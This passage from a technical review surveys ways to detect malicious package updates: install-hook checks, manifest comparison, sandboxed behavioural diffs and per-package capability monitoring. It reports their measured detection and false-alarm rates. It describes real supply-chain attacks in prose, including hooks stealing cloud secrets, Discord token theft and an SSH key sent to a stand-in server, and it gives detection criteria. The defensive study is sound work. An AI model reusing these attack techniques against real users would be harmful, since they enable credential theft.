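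These signs are easy to check, but they concern how someone published a release, not what the code can do. They can also fail when the attacker controls the build system. In June 2026, attackers published malicious versions of 32 Red Hat packages. Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Hijack Red Hat npm Scope to Steal Cloud Secrets* reports that they did so through the compromised build pipeline, using the same short-lived credentials as a genuine release. Each package had a `preinstall` hook, so checking for install hooks would have caught them even though the publishing record showed nothing unusual.

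### When the registry and the package disagree

A hook check can also read the wrong copy of `package.json`. When someone publishes a package, the npm registry receives an archive and a separate *manifest*, which describes the package, including its scripts and dependencies. JFrog's *NPM Manifest Confusion* explains that the registry didn't verify that the two matched. In 2023, Darcy Clarke, a former GitHub engineering manager, demonstrated the problem with a package whose archive had an install script and a dependency, while its manifest listed neither. npm's website and most auditing tools used the manifest, but the installer used the `package.json` in the archive.

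About six months later, JFrog's researchers had found more than 800 packages with mismatches. Only 18 were deliberate, all of them tests or demonstrations, not attacks. Most of the others had ordinary causes, such as two ways of writing the same repository address or a test script missing from the manifest. Flagging every mismatch would therefore produce mostly false alarms. JFrog considered only packages with different names, different dependencies, or differences in the scripts that run at installation or start-up.

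A detector that always reads `package.json` from the archive won't be misled about hooks. Comparing that file with the registry manifest is still worthwhile, because an install script missing from the manifest was probably hidden on purpose.

### What package managers run by default

npm ran dependencies' install hooks automatically until version 12, which came out a few days before the jscrambler attack. GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026) announces that hooks from dependencies now run only if the project explicitly allows them. The same applies to the automatic builds that Phantom Gyp exploited. npm 12 also refuses by default to install dependencies directly from Git repositories or from web addresses outside the registry. Older versions of npm continue to run hooks.

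pnpm, an alternative to npm, began blocking these scripts eighteen months before npm did, according to Robert (2026). pip still runs build code when it installs from source, although its `--only-binary` option can restrict it to wheels. Years before npm changed its default, *Wolf at the Door* (Wyss, Wittman and colleagues, 2022) presented Latch, a tool for preventing install-time attacks in npm, because long chains of dependencies make it hard to vet every installed package by hand.

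Under the new default, a reviewer should also look for new package approvals. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) describes a command for approving the packages a project trusts, which saves the approvals in the project's `package.json`. If a developer or coding agent adds a package to that list, its previously inactive install code can run with the developer's privileges. The diff may show a single line with no network call, file path or command. A detector should treat the entry as a new capability and analyse the hook it enables. For approved packages, it should still compare the hooks and the files they call, since a later release could change what a hook does.

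Blocking install hooks by default should stop many attacks. Socket writes that almost every worm and credential stealer on npm since late 2025 ran at install time. But blocking hooks has no effect on code that runs on import, and the jscrambler attacker switched to that method within minutes.

A waiting period covers both. pnpm (2025) describes a setting that blocks new versions until they reach a minimum age, and Fortuna recommends the equivalent setting in npm. The delay gives other people's detectors time to find malicious code, but it detects nothing itself. Socket flagged jscrambler 8.14.0 six minutes after it was published, and npm removed the malicious axios versions in about three hours.

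## Running both versions and comparing what they do

A search of the source finds little when the important code is encoded, compiled or still on someone's server, as it was in several of the attacks above. Running the code avoids much of this difficulty. However well an author disguises a program, it can reach a file or a server only through a *system call*, a request to the operating system. A *sandbox*, an isolated environment for running untrusted code, can record those requests. Behavioural comparison records both versions and looks for actions that only the new one takes:

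1. Put each version in its own sandbox, with the same operating system, dependencies and settings.
2. Give both versions the same inputs.
3. Record their system calls, the server names they look up, the connections they open, the programs they start and the files they change.
4. Remove details that differ from run to run, such as process numbers and the names of temporary folders.
5. Subtract the old version's list from the new version's.

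Suppose a test calls `invoice_text` for a customer in Auckland, in a sandbox that has a made-up `BILLING_API_KEY` and a stand-in for the billing server. The recording might include these entries:

| Raw record from the new version | After clean-up | Also in the old version's record? |
|---|---|---|
| opens `/usr/share/zoneinfo/Pacific/Auckland` | reads time-zone data | no |
| looks up `billing.example.com`, connects to 10.0.0.5 | contacts `billing.example.com` | no |
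| process 48213 starts `/usr/bin/sh after_invoice.sh` | starts `sh` | no |
| writes `/tmp/run-7f2a/invoice_cache.txt` | writes `invoice_cache.txt` | no |
| writes `/tmp/run-7f2a/__pycache__/invoice.pyc` | writes Python's compiled copy of the file | yes |

The last row shows why clean-up has to come before subtraction. The temporary folder gets a new random name in every run, so without clean-up, Python's routine compiled copy would always look new. But clean-up can remove too much. A detector that ignored the whole temporary folder would miss the program that the jscrambler attacker unpacked there.

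The table has no row for reading the key. The operating system passes a program its whole environment at startup, so looking up a variable later is an ordinary memory read with no system call. To record the lookup, a detector has to monitor Python itself. It can also search the outgoing traffic for the made-up key, if it can decrypt that traffic.

The stand-in server also affects what gets recorded. If the sandbox blocked the connection instead, `server.request` would raise an error and the function would stop, so the record would contain neither the shell script nor the cache file.

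Two runs of the same version can also differ, for example if a program checks for updates once a day. To remove some of these false differences, a tool can run the old version several times and report only the new version's behavior that appears in none of those runs.

### Recording behaviour across a registry

The Package Analysis project, which Brown and Wheeler announced in 2022, records how packages behave across whole registries. The Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry group, runs it. According to OpenSSF's *Package Analysis*, the software watches registries for new packages and assigns each one to a pool of workers. A worker runs the package inside gVisor, a sandbox that stands between a program and the machine's operating system. The worker records system calls with a Linux tool called strace, captures network traffic, and stores the results in a database that anyone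 can query. *Pack-A-Mal* (Vu, Nguyen and colleagues, 2025) extends this software and describes its three phases, which install the package, import it and then execute it.

*The Package Analysis Project* (Brown, 2022) describes how Google found the project's early malicious packages through simple database queries. One of them, the PyPI package discordcmd, stood out because it contacted GitHub's file server, the chat service Discord and a site that looks up IP addresses. It downloaded a back door, installed it in the user's Discord program and stole the user's login token. Many of the others contacted domains that people commonly use to receive data from test attacks, and the same domains appeared across unrelated packages.

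These finds are good evidence that recording works, but they didn't depend on comparing versions. Many of the packages were imitations with no earlier release to compare them with. OpenSSF describes the project as tracking how packages change over time, but Brown and Wheeler listed detecting such differences as a future goal. The project has remained a useful source of reports. By October 2023, OpenSSF's repository of known malicious packages listed more than 15,000, and Brown and Kadouri (2023) name Package Analysis as one of three sources, without saying how many each contributed.

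Packages run in bulk also fail fairly often. *QUT-DV25* (2025) covers 14,271 Python packages, about half of them malicious. Roughly 88% of the 14,271 installed successfully, and the rest crashed, looped forever, shut down or stopped to ask for a password. A detector has to report such packages as "did not run", because an empty recording would otherwise look like harmless behaviour.

Another practical decision is whether to let the sandbox reach the internet. Vu and colleagues demonstrated their system on a malicious version of @solana/web3.js, a cryptocurrency library, after adding code to steal more files. The malware sent an SSH key (a credential for logging in to other machines) from the sandbox to their stand-in for the attacker's server, so the recording covered the whole theft. An open connection to a real attacker could leak anything valuable in the sandbox or let the malware attack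 other machines. Blocking the connection is safer but can stop the malware before it does anything else worth recording.

### Testing an update through one application

*Preflight* describes a system for Python that checks whether a new version of a package does anything new when one particular application uses it, rather than judging the package as a whole. The system first parses the application and lists the functions and classes that the application refers to in each package. It also reads the exact version of each package from the project's dependency files and rejects any dependency without a fixed version, because the verdict applies only to the version that ran.

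Next, a small language model, GPT-5.4 mini, writes a *harness*, a short Python program that calls those functions. An ordinary program then checks that the harness is valid Python of at most 100 lines, imports the package and calls every function on the list. If the harness fails the check, the model can revise it once. In the evaluation, four of the nine harnesses passed on the first attempt and the other five passed after one revision, at a total cost of about 3 cents. The model never sees the recordings, so it can't use them to write a better harness.

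Preflight runs the harness in a restricted Docker container, an isolated environment that shares the host machine's operating-system kernel. It records system calls and network traffic, compares the file system before and after, and sends name lookups to a *sinkhole*, an internal server that keeps the traffic from reaching the internet. It then reduces each recording to a list of the servers contacted, sensitive environment variables read, lasting file changes, programs started and kinds of system call. The comparison is a set difference, written with a backslash:

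```
Δ_A(P_v, P_b) = F(P_v, A) \ F(P_b, A)
```

Here `P_v` is the new version of the package, `P_b` is the baseline, and `A` is the application. `F(P, A)` is the set of capabilities that Preflight observes when it runs version `P` through the functions that `A` uses. Each server and program is a separate element, so a changed host name counts as a new capability even if the old version already used the network.

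Preflight treats some new elements as critical, including unfamiliar servers, newly started programs, lasting file changes and access to variables that hold credentials. Two or more critical findings give the verdict *malicious*, one gives *suspicious* and none gives *clean*. A critical finding from a static scan can override this rule, but that didn't happen in any of the five main tests. The researchers also planned for a larger language model to assess the evidence, but each request exceeded the model's input limit, so every verdict depended only on the number of critical findings.

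The five tests used packages from four real attacks:

| Application context | Versions compared | Critical findings | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| LiteLLM client | 1.82.6 → 1.82.7 | none | clean |
| LiteLLM proxy | 1.82.6 → 1.82.7 | 2 servers, 12 programs | malicious |
| Ultralytics | 8.3.40 → 8.3.41 | 3 servers, 3 paths to the download tool curl | malicious |
| ctx | 0.1.2 → 0.2.2 | 3 servers | malicious |
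| DurableTask | no baseline | 3 servers | malicious |

LiteLLM is a library for calling language models from different providers. It can also run as a proxy, a server that passes on other programs' requests. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) places the malicious code of version 1.82.7 in `proxy_server.py`. An application that only uses the client never loads that file, so the clean verdict is correct for that application. But the code would still steal credentials if a developer later started the proxy in the same project, so most reviewers would presumably want to reject the version for both uses.

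The next release, 1.82.8, added a `.pth` file, which Python runs whenever it starts. Willison (2026), in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8*, points out that installing this version was enough to trigger the theft, without importing LiteLLM. Preflight's client test might therefore have caught it, but the researchers didn't test that version.

The four malicious verdicts are weaker evidence than they seem because the researchers knew which code was affected. They chose the client context in advance, then added the proxy context as an exploratory test that would reach that code. Someone checking an unknown update wouldn't know which contexts to test.

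The DurableTask verdict depends on a counting error. Of the three servers counted, only check.git-service.com belonged to the attacker. The other two were the sandbox's own sinkhole and Docker's name server. Without those two, the rule would have returned *suspicious*. The same error may have affected ctx, because the paper describes one new server but counts three. A baseline removes these addresses only if the old version also looks up a server, so the detector should exclude them explicitly.

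The DurableTask test had no baseline because, according to the researchers, no earlier version could be defended as harmless. But OSV's *PYSEC-2026-207* (2026), the public advisory on the attack, mentions known-good versions that remained available, so a comparison may have been possible. Without a comparison, the result shows what the package did but not which of that behavior was new in the update.

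The researchers also listed the kinds of behaviour they expected to see in each attack. They expected nine findings across the four malicious cases, and Preflight observed four. The five it did not observe included both expected reads of environment variables and both expected file changes. The sandbox may have stopped some attacks before they reached those steps. Preflight looks for new reads of secrets, but these results provide no evidence that it can detect them.

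### Calling functions instead of only importing them

A simpler harness would only import the package. The researchers compared the two approaches on ctx and Ultralytics, a computer-vision package, and kept everything else the same. Calling the application's functions exposed both attacks, while importing the packages exposed neither. The malicious code in Ultralytics ran when the program created a model, and the malicious code in ctx ran when the program created a `Ctx` object.

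Two packages are enough to show that an import-only test can miss an attack, but not how often it does. The researchers could have picked DurableTask, for example, whose malicious code ran on import, according to OSV. The test also didn't compare harnesses written by a language model with ones from a person or a template, so it doesn't show that the model's are better.

Preflight gave clean verdicts to all 100 harmless packages in a separate test. This doesn't establish a false-positive rate of zero. If the true rate is p, and the packages are a random sample, the probability of seeing no flags in 100 tests is:

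```
(1 − p)^100
```

A detector that wrongly flags 3% of packages (p = 3%) would still get a perfect score about 4.8% of the time, or about once in 20 attempts. By the usual 95% standard, the result is therefore compatible with any true false-alarm rate up to about 3%. At that rate, a team that checks 200 package updates a month could see six false alarms.

The 100 packages weren't a random sample, since the researchers picked them from packages related to AI and data. The paper doesn't say how many of these tests compared two versions. A package is also more likely to get a clean verdict when the harness runs little of its code, so the result would be more informative with a measure of how much code ran.

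### Recording each package separately

Like a program-level static comparison, a recording of the whole program misses a capability that is new to one package if another package already had it. *GoLeash* (Cesarano, Monperrus and Natella, 2025) describes a system that keeps a separate record for each package in a running Go program.

Go combines all the packages into one executable file, so the operating system can't tell which package made a system call. GoLeash uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small monitoring programs inside the operating system, to save the *stack trace* (the chain of function calls in progress) at each system call. It starts from the most recent function, skips Go's standard library, and attributes the system call to the first function that belongs to the application or a dependency.

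GoLeash has two modes. In analysis mode, it runs the application on normal work, such as its integration tests (which exercise several parts of a program together), and saves an allowlist with this structure:

```
package → capability → call paths that led to it
```

In enforcement mode, the tool checks each later system call against the allowlist and either logs a violation or stops the program. Using the old version to build the allowlist and then running the new version in enforcement mode effectively compares the two.

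The call paths reveal a change that capabilities alone would miss. In a Go version of the `notify` change, the alerts package could already use the network, so its capabilities would stay the same. GoLeash would still report a violation, because the path from the invoice package to the network is new. It would not detect the invoice package sending the same kind of data to a different server, because it doesn't check addresses. Like Preflight, GoLeash distinguishes reading a file from writing one only when the program performs the operation, but GoLeash doesn't record which file.

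Cesarano and colleagues tested GoLeash on five large projects, including Kubernetes. They ran each project normally to build the allowlist. Then they added one of five malicious behaviours to one package at a time, rebuilt the project and ran it again. The behaviours imitated real attacks, such as sending system settings to a server or downloading a malicious file. Adding each behaviour to each of the 653 packages produced 3,265 malicious variants.

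GoLeash detected an average of 98% of the variants across the 25 combinations of project and behaviour, compared with 32% for a single allowlist covering the whole application. Pooling the variants gives 99% and 36%. The application-wide list missed every variant of three behaviours, including the data theft and the download, because each project already used the necessary capabilities somewhere. GoLeash missed variants in which the package itself already used the necessary capabilities. This happens less often, since the median package in Kubernetes used only three capabilities.

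Disguising the code had little effect on detection overall. The researchers hid two of the behaviours in four ways, for example by writing them in C or putting them in a separate program. Average detection rates stayed between 92% and 100%, although the rate was 77% for data theft written in C and added to frp, a networking tool.

These rates don't cover code that never runs, because the researchers inserted the malicious code only into functions they had already seen running, and they used the same workload to build the allowlist and test the variants. The original applications caused no false alarms, but the researchers acknowledge that this follows from the design, because harmless code doing the same work uses the same capabilities. The experiment doesn't show how often a harmless new version or an unusual request would break the rules.

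Monitoring increased processor time per request by 1.3% to 5.1%, which is low enough to leave it on in many production systems.

### What running and reading each find

The same experiment compares GoLeash with Capslock, which reads the code and follows possible calls. For Capslock, a variant counted as detected if the malicious code needed a capability that Capslock hadn't already found in the package. Adding up the results for undisguised data theft across the five projects gives these totals:

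| Packages | Number | Caught by GoLeash | Caught by Capslock |
|---|---|---|---|
| Visible to both tools | 288 | 284 | 176 |
| Visible only to GoLeash | 365 | 364 | – |
| Visible only to Capslock | 1,056 | – | 725 |

On the packages both tools could analyse, GoLeash caught 99% of the variants and Capslock caught 61%. Capslock missed more partly because its categories are broad and don't separate reading a file from writing one.

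Cesarano and colleagues also report an average advantage of 65 percentage points for GoLeash, and describe the comparison as putting both tools on an equal footing. But that figure covers all 653 packages that ran, and it matches the underlying numbers only if the 365 packages that Capslock couldn't analyse count as misses. They attribute most of these gaps to reflection and plug-ins. The 99% and 61% are a fairer measure of how well each tool performs on packages it can analyse.

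The last row matters most for a reviewer. More than half of the packages in the table never ran during the tests, so GoLeash had no record of them. Capslock caught the malicious code in 69% of those packages. Neither tool can replace the other. The researchers suggest using Capslock to list capabilities that a program can reach but didn't use during testing, so a developer can review them before turning on enforcement.

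### Code that doesn't run during the test

Recording an action proves that the code can perform it, but an empty recording may only mean that the test didn't reach the relevant line. Some code also waits before acting. Vu and colleagues kept Package Analysis's default execution time of 10 seconds, so a program that did nothing suspicious for the first minute would have looked harmless.

Other code behaves differently depending on the machine it runs on. One version of node-ipc, for example, checked the path of the program's main file. According to OSV, the malicious DurableTask versions downloaded software with a component that destroyed data only in certain locations. Code can also check the date, the user's name, the operating system, or whether it seems to be in a sandbox. Plenty of harmless code makes similar checks, for example to run a monthly report or apply a fix for Windows.

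Testers can change the sandbox's clock, run the code on several operating systems and supply realistic fake credentials, but these steps cover only the conditions that someone thought of. Monitoring in production, which GoLeash allows, can catch delayed behaviour when it happens, but by then the code is running on a machine with real data.

When a team changes its own code, it can use its existing tests as the input for both versions. These tests already do things like create an invoice or log in a user, so developers don't have to write anything new. Even a test that checks only the invoice's date is useful, because the shell script still runs during the test and the recording includes it.

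The detector should run the same tests on both versions, normally those from before the change. If it also runs the author's added tests on the new version, a connection could look new only because an added test exercised old code. The added tests are worth running on the new version, and on the old version where they work, but the detector should report those results separately.

Tests can hide network access when they replace a connection with a *mock*, a fake object that returns a fixed answer. Developers often do this so that tests run quickly and don't depend on an outside server. If a test replaces `HTTPSConnection` with a mock, the new invoice code appears to work but makes no connection, so the recording contains no network access. Removing the mock would reveal the attempt, though the test might then fail.

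Tests also tend to cover ordinary cases. Suppose the change adds this:

```python
if inv.total > 10_000:
    upload(inv)
```

If every invoice in the tests is for less than 10,000, the upload never happens. A harness that calls `invoice_text` once, as Preflight's might, has the same problem, because one call doesn't run every branch of the function. Cesarano and colleagues suggest *fuzzing*, which means running the program on many automatically generated inputs. Fuzzing would probably trigger this upload quickly, but not one that depends on a particular customer's name.

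A *coverage* tool records which lines run during a test, so it can show where the recording is incomplete. For the code above, it would mark the call to `upload` as not run. A detector could then use static analysis to check that line and the functions it calls, and report that the program can reach the upload but didn't perform it in the test. If the static analysis can't resolve the call either, the detector should report "unknown" for that line, even if every test passed and the two recordings are identical.

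## How often harmless package updates are flagged

Harmless updates also add capabilities, so a detector that compares versions will flag some of them even if it works perfectly. The most detailed figures come from *You Can Run But You Can't Hide* (Ohm, Pohl and Boes, 2023), which describes a system that limits a Node.js package to the capabilities of an earlier version that the user trusts. The system parses the JavaScript files of the package and its dependencies, and lists the built-in modules they import and the global objects they use. When the user runs an update, a modified copy of Node.js replaces any module or object that isn't on the list with a dummy that does nothing.

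JavaScript code can use global objects without importing them. One of them, `process`, gives access to environment variables, while another, `Buffer`, only handles raw bytes in memory. The system counts each built-in module and each global object as one capability. A finer setting counts their individual members, so `fs.readFile` and `fs.writeFile`, both in the file-system module `fs`, become separate capabilities.

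To see how this would affect ordinary updates, the researchers examined past releases of the 1,000 npm packages that other packages depend on most. They assumed every version still on npm was harmless. They counted patch updates (meant only to fix bugs), minor updates (which can add features) and major updates separately.

| Kind of update | Adds a module or global object | Adds a module, global object or member |
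|---|---|---|
| Patch | 14.7% | 20.3% |
| Minor | 40.2% | 49.6% |
| Major | 62.5% | 65.9% |

(The paper prints 20.4% for the finer patch figure, but also gives 79.7% as the share of patch updates that added nothing.)

Ohm and colleagues consider even the patch rate too high for their system. They point out that a blocked capability may belong to code the application never runs, so some flagged updates would still work, but they didn't test how many.

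As with Froh and colleagues' 1.4%, a flag can be a false alarm about malware but still correctly identify a new capability. Many of the additions would not interest a reviewer, though. In the coarser setting, 21.9% of minor updates and 22.4% of major updates added global objects but no modules. Excluding those updates lowers the rates to 18.3% for minor updates and 40.1% for major ones, and the remaining additions can still include modules such as `path`, which only edits the text of file paths.

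The researchers also tested the system on ten past attacks, including the ones on rate-map, conventional-changelog and event-stream. For each, they listed the capabilities of the last clean version and then ran the malicious version in a sandbox. The system stopped nine. They couldn't trigger the malicious behaviour of the tenth, load-from-cwd-or-npm, so they didn't count it as stopped. In five of the nine cases, the program crashed because it couldn't handle the dummy objects.

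In this test, the finer setting flagged more harmless updates but stopped no additional attacks, because the clean versions hadn't used the modules or objects that the attackers needed. But ten attacks are a small sample, and the researchers had excluded any that only worked in a browser, the kind that made up most of RogueOne's second test set. The protection also doesn't cover packages in JavaScript's newer module format, which account for 13.3% of the 1,000 popular packages.

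### A much lower rate for Go

In 2024, McClintock and Dethridge reported that less than 2% of version updates to Go packages add a capability, based on Capslock's results on deps.dev. They don't give the number of updates, the period covered, or the mix of patch, minor and major versions. The mix can't explain the whole difference from npm, because even npm's patch updates added capabilities more than seven times as often as Go updates did.

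Part of the gap probably comes from how each study defines a capability. A Node.js package that already uses the `http` module and starts using `https` gains a capability in the npm study, but a Go package that makes the equivalent change already has Capslock's NETWORK capability. The npm study's two settings cover the same updates, so comparing them gives some idea of how much the definition matters. Counting individual members raised the patch rate by more than a third. Neither setting groups modules into broad categories as Capslock does, so the study doesn't show how much that would lower the rate.

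Capslock follows possible calls through Go code, whereas the npm system looks for names in JavaScript files. Capslock also counts capabilities that a program can reach but never uses. This could lead it to flag fewer updates, because a package that appears to have file and network access from its first release has fewer new capabilities to gain later.

Dependencies could raise or lower the Go rate. Capslock includes capabilities that a package reaches through other packages, so updating a dependency can add a capability. But if the package already reaches the network through one dependency, a second dependency that uses the network adds no new capability. The npm system keeps a separate list for each package in the dependency tree, but Ohm and colleagues don't explain exactly how changes to those lists affected their update rates.

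The samples also have little in common. The npm study examined heavily used packages, while deps.dev covers Go packages more generally, presumably including many small ones that rarely change. What counts as one update may also differ. A Go *module* is a group of packages that share a version number. If McClintock and Dethridge counted each package separately, one release of a module with 20 packages would count as 20 updates, and most of them might contain no relevant change.

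Neither study isolates the cause. That would require applying both vocabularies to the same releases and separately varying how dependencies are treated. A team choosing a detector would learn more from running the tool on its own past updates than from relying on either figure.

### From error rates to precision

When real cases are rare, even a low false-positive rate can produce mostly false alarms. Suppose a detector checks N updates, and a fraction f of them are real cases. With recall r and false-positive rate p, it correctly flags N × f × r updates and wrongly flags N × (1 − f) × p. Precision is the correct flags divided by all flags, and N cancels out:

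```
precision = (f × r) / (f × r + (1 − f) × p)
```

Froh and colleagues' tool flagged 1.4% of npm updates in 2023. Treating all of those flags as errors gives a false positive rate of 1.4%. At that rate, and assuming perfect recall, if one update in 10,000 is malicious, checking 10,000 updates would produce one correct flag and about 140 false ones, a precision of about 0.7%. If one update in 50 is malicious, checking 5,000 would produce 100 correct flags and about 69 false ones, a precision of about 59%.

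The table gives the precision for other combinations, again with perfect recall. The last column uses Ohm and colleagues' rate for patch updates.

| Frequency of real cases | 0.1% false-positive rate | 1.4% | 14.7% |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 10,000 | 9% | 0.7% | 0.07% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 50% | 6.7% | 0.7% |
| 1 in 50 | 95% | 59% | 12% |

The last row might suit a search for unrequested capabilities, which are presumably more common than malware. The false-positive rate would have to be measured again, though, because some updates that are false positives in a search for malware would be correct detections in this one.

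If a detector catches every real case, about half its flags are correct when its false-positive rate equals the frequency of real cases. For something that occurs once in 10,000 updates, that rate is about 0.01%. RogueOne's rate of about 5% and GPT-4o's 0.4% are far higher. Preflight flagged none of 100 harmless packages, but that sample is too small to show a rate as low as 0.01%. Showing such a rate with the same 95% confidence as before would take about 30,000 harmless updates with no flags.

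### Scanners for Python packages

The people who run PyPI want an even lower rate. Vu, Newman and Meyers interviewed two people from the PyPI maintainer community and an academic researcher for *A Benchmark Comparison of Python Malware Detection Approaches* (2022), which appeared at a conference in 2023 as *Bad Snakes*. At the time, PyPI received about 20,000 releases a week, and its administrators removed about 20 malicious packages. They had about 20 minutes a week for malware reports, and each report took roughly a minute.

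PyPI's administrators considered even a false-positive rate of 0.01%, or two false alarms a week, unacceptable because reports of real malware already took up all their available time. PyPI introduced its own malware checks in 2020, and the administrators turned them off two years later.

Vu and colleagues tested those checks and two other static scanners, Microsoft's OSS Detect Backdoor and the Python tool Bandit4Mal. The table shows the share of packages with at least one alert when each tool scanned every Python file.

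| Scanner | 168 malicious packages | 1,430 popular packages | 986 random packages |
|---|---|---|---|
| PyPI's checks | 85.7% | 94.2% | 67.8% |
| OSS Detect Backdoor | 85.1% | 96.6% | 77.2% |
| Bandit4Mal | 90.5% | 96.6% | 84.6% |

All three flagged popular packages more often than malware, probably because popular packages contain much more code. When PyPI's checks scanned only `setup.py`, they flagged fewer packages, 33.2% of popular ones and 14.9% of random ones, but caught only 58.9% of the malware. Requiring several alerts before flagging a package didn't solve the problem either, because it also discarded too many correct flags.

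The researchers also looked at which of PyPI's rules produced the alerts in `setup.py`. The network rule was more useful for telling malicious packages from harmless ones than the rules for starting processes, which matched about as often in both.

The researchers assumed that the popular packages were harmless, since people usually find malware in such packages quickly, and they accepted that the random sample might contain a few malicious ones. They scanned only the latest version of each package, so the rates are for whole-package scans and would overstate the number of flags from a comparison between versions that leaves out old findings.

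Later studies have retested some of these tools without repeating the full study. In *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026), OSSGadget, the collection that includes OSS Detect Backdoor, flagged 734 of 953 benign npm packages (77%). That rate is almost the same as the 2022 figure for random Python packages.

*How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (2026) also tests OSSGadget and ten other tools. Precision ranges from about 50% to 99.9%, but 47% of the packages in the benchmark are malicious, so a tool that flagged everything would have a precision of 47%. The harmless packages are the latest versions of popular ones, and the researchers checked only that none appeared in either of two databases of known malware. They checked the malicious samples more carefully, with three experts reviewing 7,787 versions that earlier sources had labelled malicious and removing 1,367 (18%) as mislabelled.

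Tests on a registry's actual uploads avoid the artificial mix. In *One Detector Fits All*, Montaruli, Compagna and colleagues (2025) trained a classifier and ran it on about 91,800 PyPI releases from 31 March to 6 May 2025. They identified 216 malicious releases, or one in 425, by using public malware databases and reviewing the releases their detectors flagged, and assumed the rest were harmless. The table shows the results at three settings.

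| Maximum false-positive rate | Malicious releases found (of 216) | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10% | 196 | 9,152 | 2.1% |
| 1% | 180 | 781 | 18.7% |
| 0.1% | 92 | 81 | 53.2% |

Going from the second setting to the third eliminated about nine-tenths of the false alarms, but also almost half the detections. A registry might accept that, because its administrators don't expect a scanner to catch everything.

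A company has far fewer releases to check. Over the same 37 days, Montaruli and colleagues ran the classifier on 1,596 releases of 584 Python packages used by a multinational software company. At the 10% setting, it flagged 46 releases (2.9%), or a little more than one a day. None of those packages had a known attack during the test, so precision was zero, but the workload was manageable. The same setting flagged about 10% of harmless releases across PyPI, so the choice of packages alone changed the false-positive rate more than threefold.

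*MalGuard* (2025) reports much higher precision in another test on PyPI uploads. Of 64,348 packages from December 2024 and January 2025, the detector flagged 144, and reviewers confirmed that 113 of those (78%) were malicious. Most of the false alarms were harmless demos that made web requests or started processes, which a capability detector would be correct to report. If all the unflagged packages were harmless, the false-positive rate was about 0.05%. Nobody reviewed those packages, though, so the test doesn't establish how much malware the detector missed.

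### Scanners for Linux packages

A Linux distribution is an operating system with a collection of packages, most of which its maintainers build from other projects' source code. Two years after the PyPI interviews, Vu, Dunlap and colleagues spoke to seven maintainers from Alpine, Arch, Debian, Ubuntu and Wolfi for *A Study of Malware Prevention in Linux Distributions* (2024). All seven saw the xz-utils backdoor, discovered that year, as a turning point.

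Until then, the distributions had relied mainly on signing packages and on reproducible builds, which let other people rebuild a package and check that it matches its source. Some interviewees thought slow release schedules also helped by leaving time for review. After the backdoor, their communities discussed verifying contributors' identities, but the interviewees opposed the idea and doubted it would work. Most were also sceptical of malware scanners, partly because of the cost and because someone would have to review the alerts.

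Only Wolfi scanned its packages. It compares malcontent's alerts for each update with those for the previous version, and blocks the update until someone reviews any new high or critical alerts. Three of the researchers worked for Chainguard, the company behind both Wolfi and malcontent, though their results were unfavorable to malcontent.

One study tested five scanners on 30 known malicious packages from npm, PyPI and RubyGems (the registry for the Ruby language), and on the source code of Wolfi projects, which it assumed were harmless. The plan was to review only a sample of the alerts by hand. One alert was enough to flag a project, but for malcontent only high and critical alerts counted.

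| Scanner | Known malicious packages flagged | Wolfi projects flagged |
|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 22 of 30 (73%) | 59 of 1,855 (3.2%) |
| malcontent | 16 of 30 (53%) | 934 of 1,856 (50%) |
| OSS Detect Backdoor | 29 of 30 (97%) | 1,046 of 1,775 (59%) |
| Packj | 18 of 29 (62%) | 790 of 1,183 (67%) |
| Bandit4Mal (Python only) | 4 of 10 (40%) | 286 of 891 (32%) |

The totals vary because some tools failed on some projects. Vu and colleagues conclude that no tool detected more than 70% of the malware, but VirusTotal and OSS Detect Backdoor both exceeded that in this test. Packj and malcontent flagged harmless projects about as often as malicious ones, so their results were close to random guessing.

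VirusTotal, a website that combines the verdicts of nearly 90 security vendors, has an advantage with malware that those vendors have already seen. In another test, the researchers inserted malicious code into 30 projects. VirusTotal flagged 21 of the projects when it scanned their source code, but only 9 when it scanned the Linux packages built from them.

The study's researchers used malcontent and Capslock to compare consecutive versions of ten Go projects. They took five consecutive versions of each project and put malicious code in the third. This gave 40 comparisons, and the malicious code was new in ten of them. Capslock flagged six of these ten and malcontent flagged four. Of the other 30, Capslock flagged 12 and malcontent flagged 8, for false-positive rates of 40% and 27%.

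Capslock's 40% is surprisingly high compared with the figure of less than 2% on deps.dev, since both come from the same tool and language. One possible reason is that ten of the 30 supposedly harmless comparisons go from the malicious third version to the clean fourth. The researchers don't say whether they counted an alert that disappeared as a difference. If they did, those ten could account for most of Capslock's 12 false positives, leaving as few as two among the 20 ordinary updates. A sample of 20 is too small to determine whether the true rate is closer to 2% or 20%.

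Both tools had a precision of 33%, which was that high only because a quarter of the comparisons added malicious code. If one update in 10,000 were malicious, Capslock's precision would fall to about 0.015% with the same recall and false-positive rate. Reviewing alerts could also take more work than the number of flagged updates suggests. Capslock produced 853 alerts, or about 47 for each comparison it flagged, while malcontent produced 21, fewer than two per flagged comparison.

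## Why ordinary application code is harder

Most measurements so far come from packages, which usually do one job. An application such as an online shop does many unrelated jobs. A typical one already reads settings from environment variables, queries a database over the network, writes files and starts a few helper programs. Its purpose also keeps changing. When a team adds card payments, for example, the program is supposed to contact a new server. A detector may therefore miss a new use of the network because the program already uses it, and any new use it does flag is probably one that somebody requested.

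The first failure comes from combining findings. Ohm and colleagues define a package's capabilities as the union of the capabilities of all its files, and a whole-program list works the same way. A capability is new to the program only if no file had it before. Suppose each file has a 10% chance of using the network, independently of the others. The chance that a program with n files doesn't use the network at all is:

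```
(1 − 0.1)^n      5 files: 59%      50 files: 0.5%
```

Files in a real program aren't independent, since teams often put network code in a few places, but the list of access types the program uses still fills up as it grows. Once the list is full, comparing the whole program before and after a change finds nothing new. Runtime controls have the same problem, which is why the application-wide list that Cesarano and colleagues tested caught only about a third of the inserted attacks.

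### Ordinary projects with full lists

Application Inspector, a free scanner that Microsoft announced in January 2020, searches source code for hundreds of patterns and labels each match with a tag, such as one for writing files. Microsoft says it uses the tool to find changes between versions of a component, which can indicate "anything from an increased attack surface to a malicious backdoor". According to Microsoft's documentation, the `tagdiff` command compares the unique tags of two source folders, so it compares which tags appear anywhere in each program.

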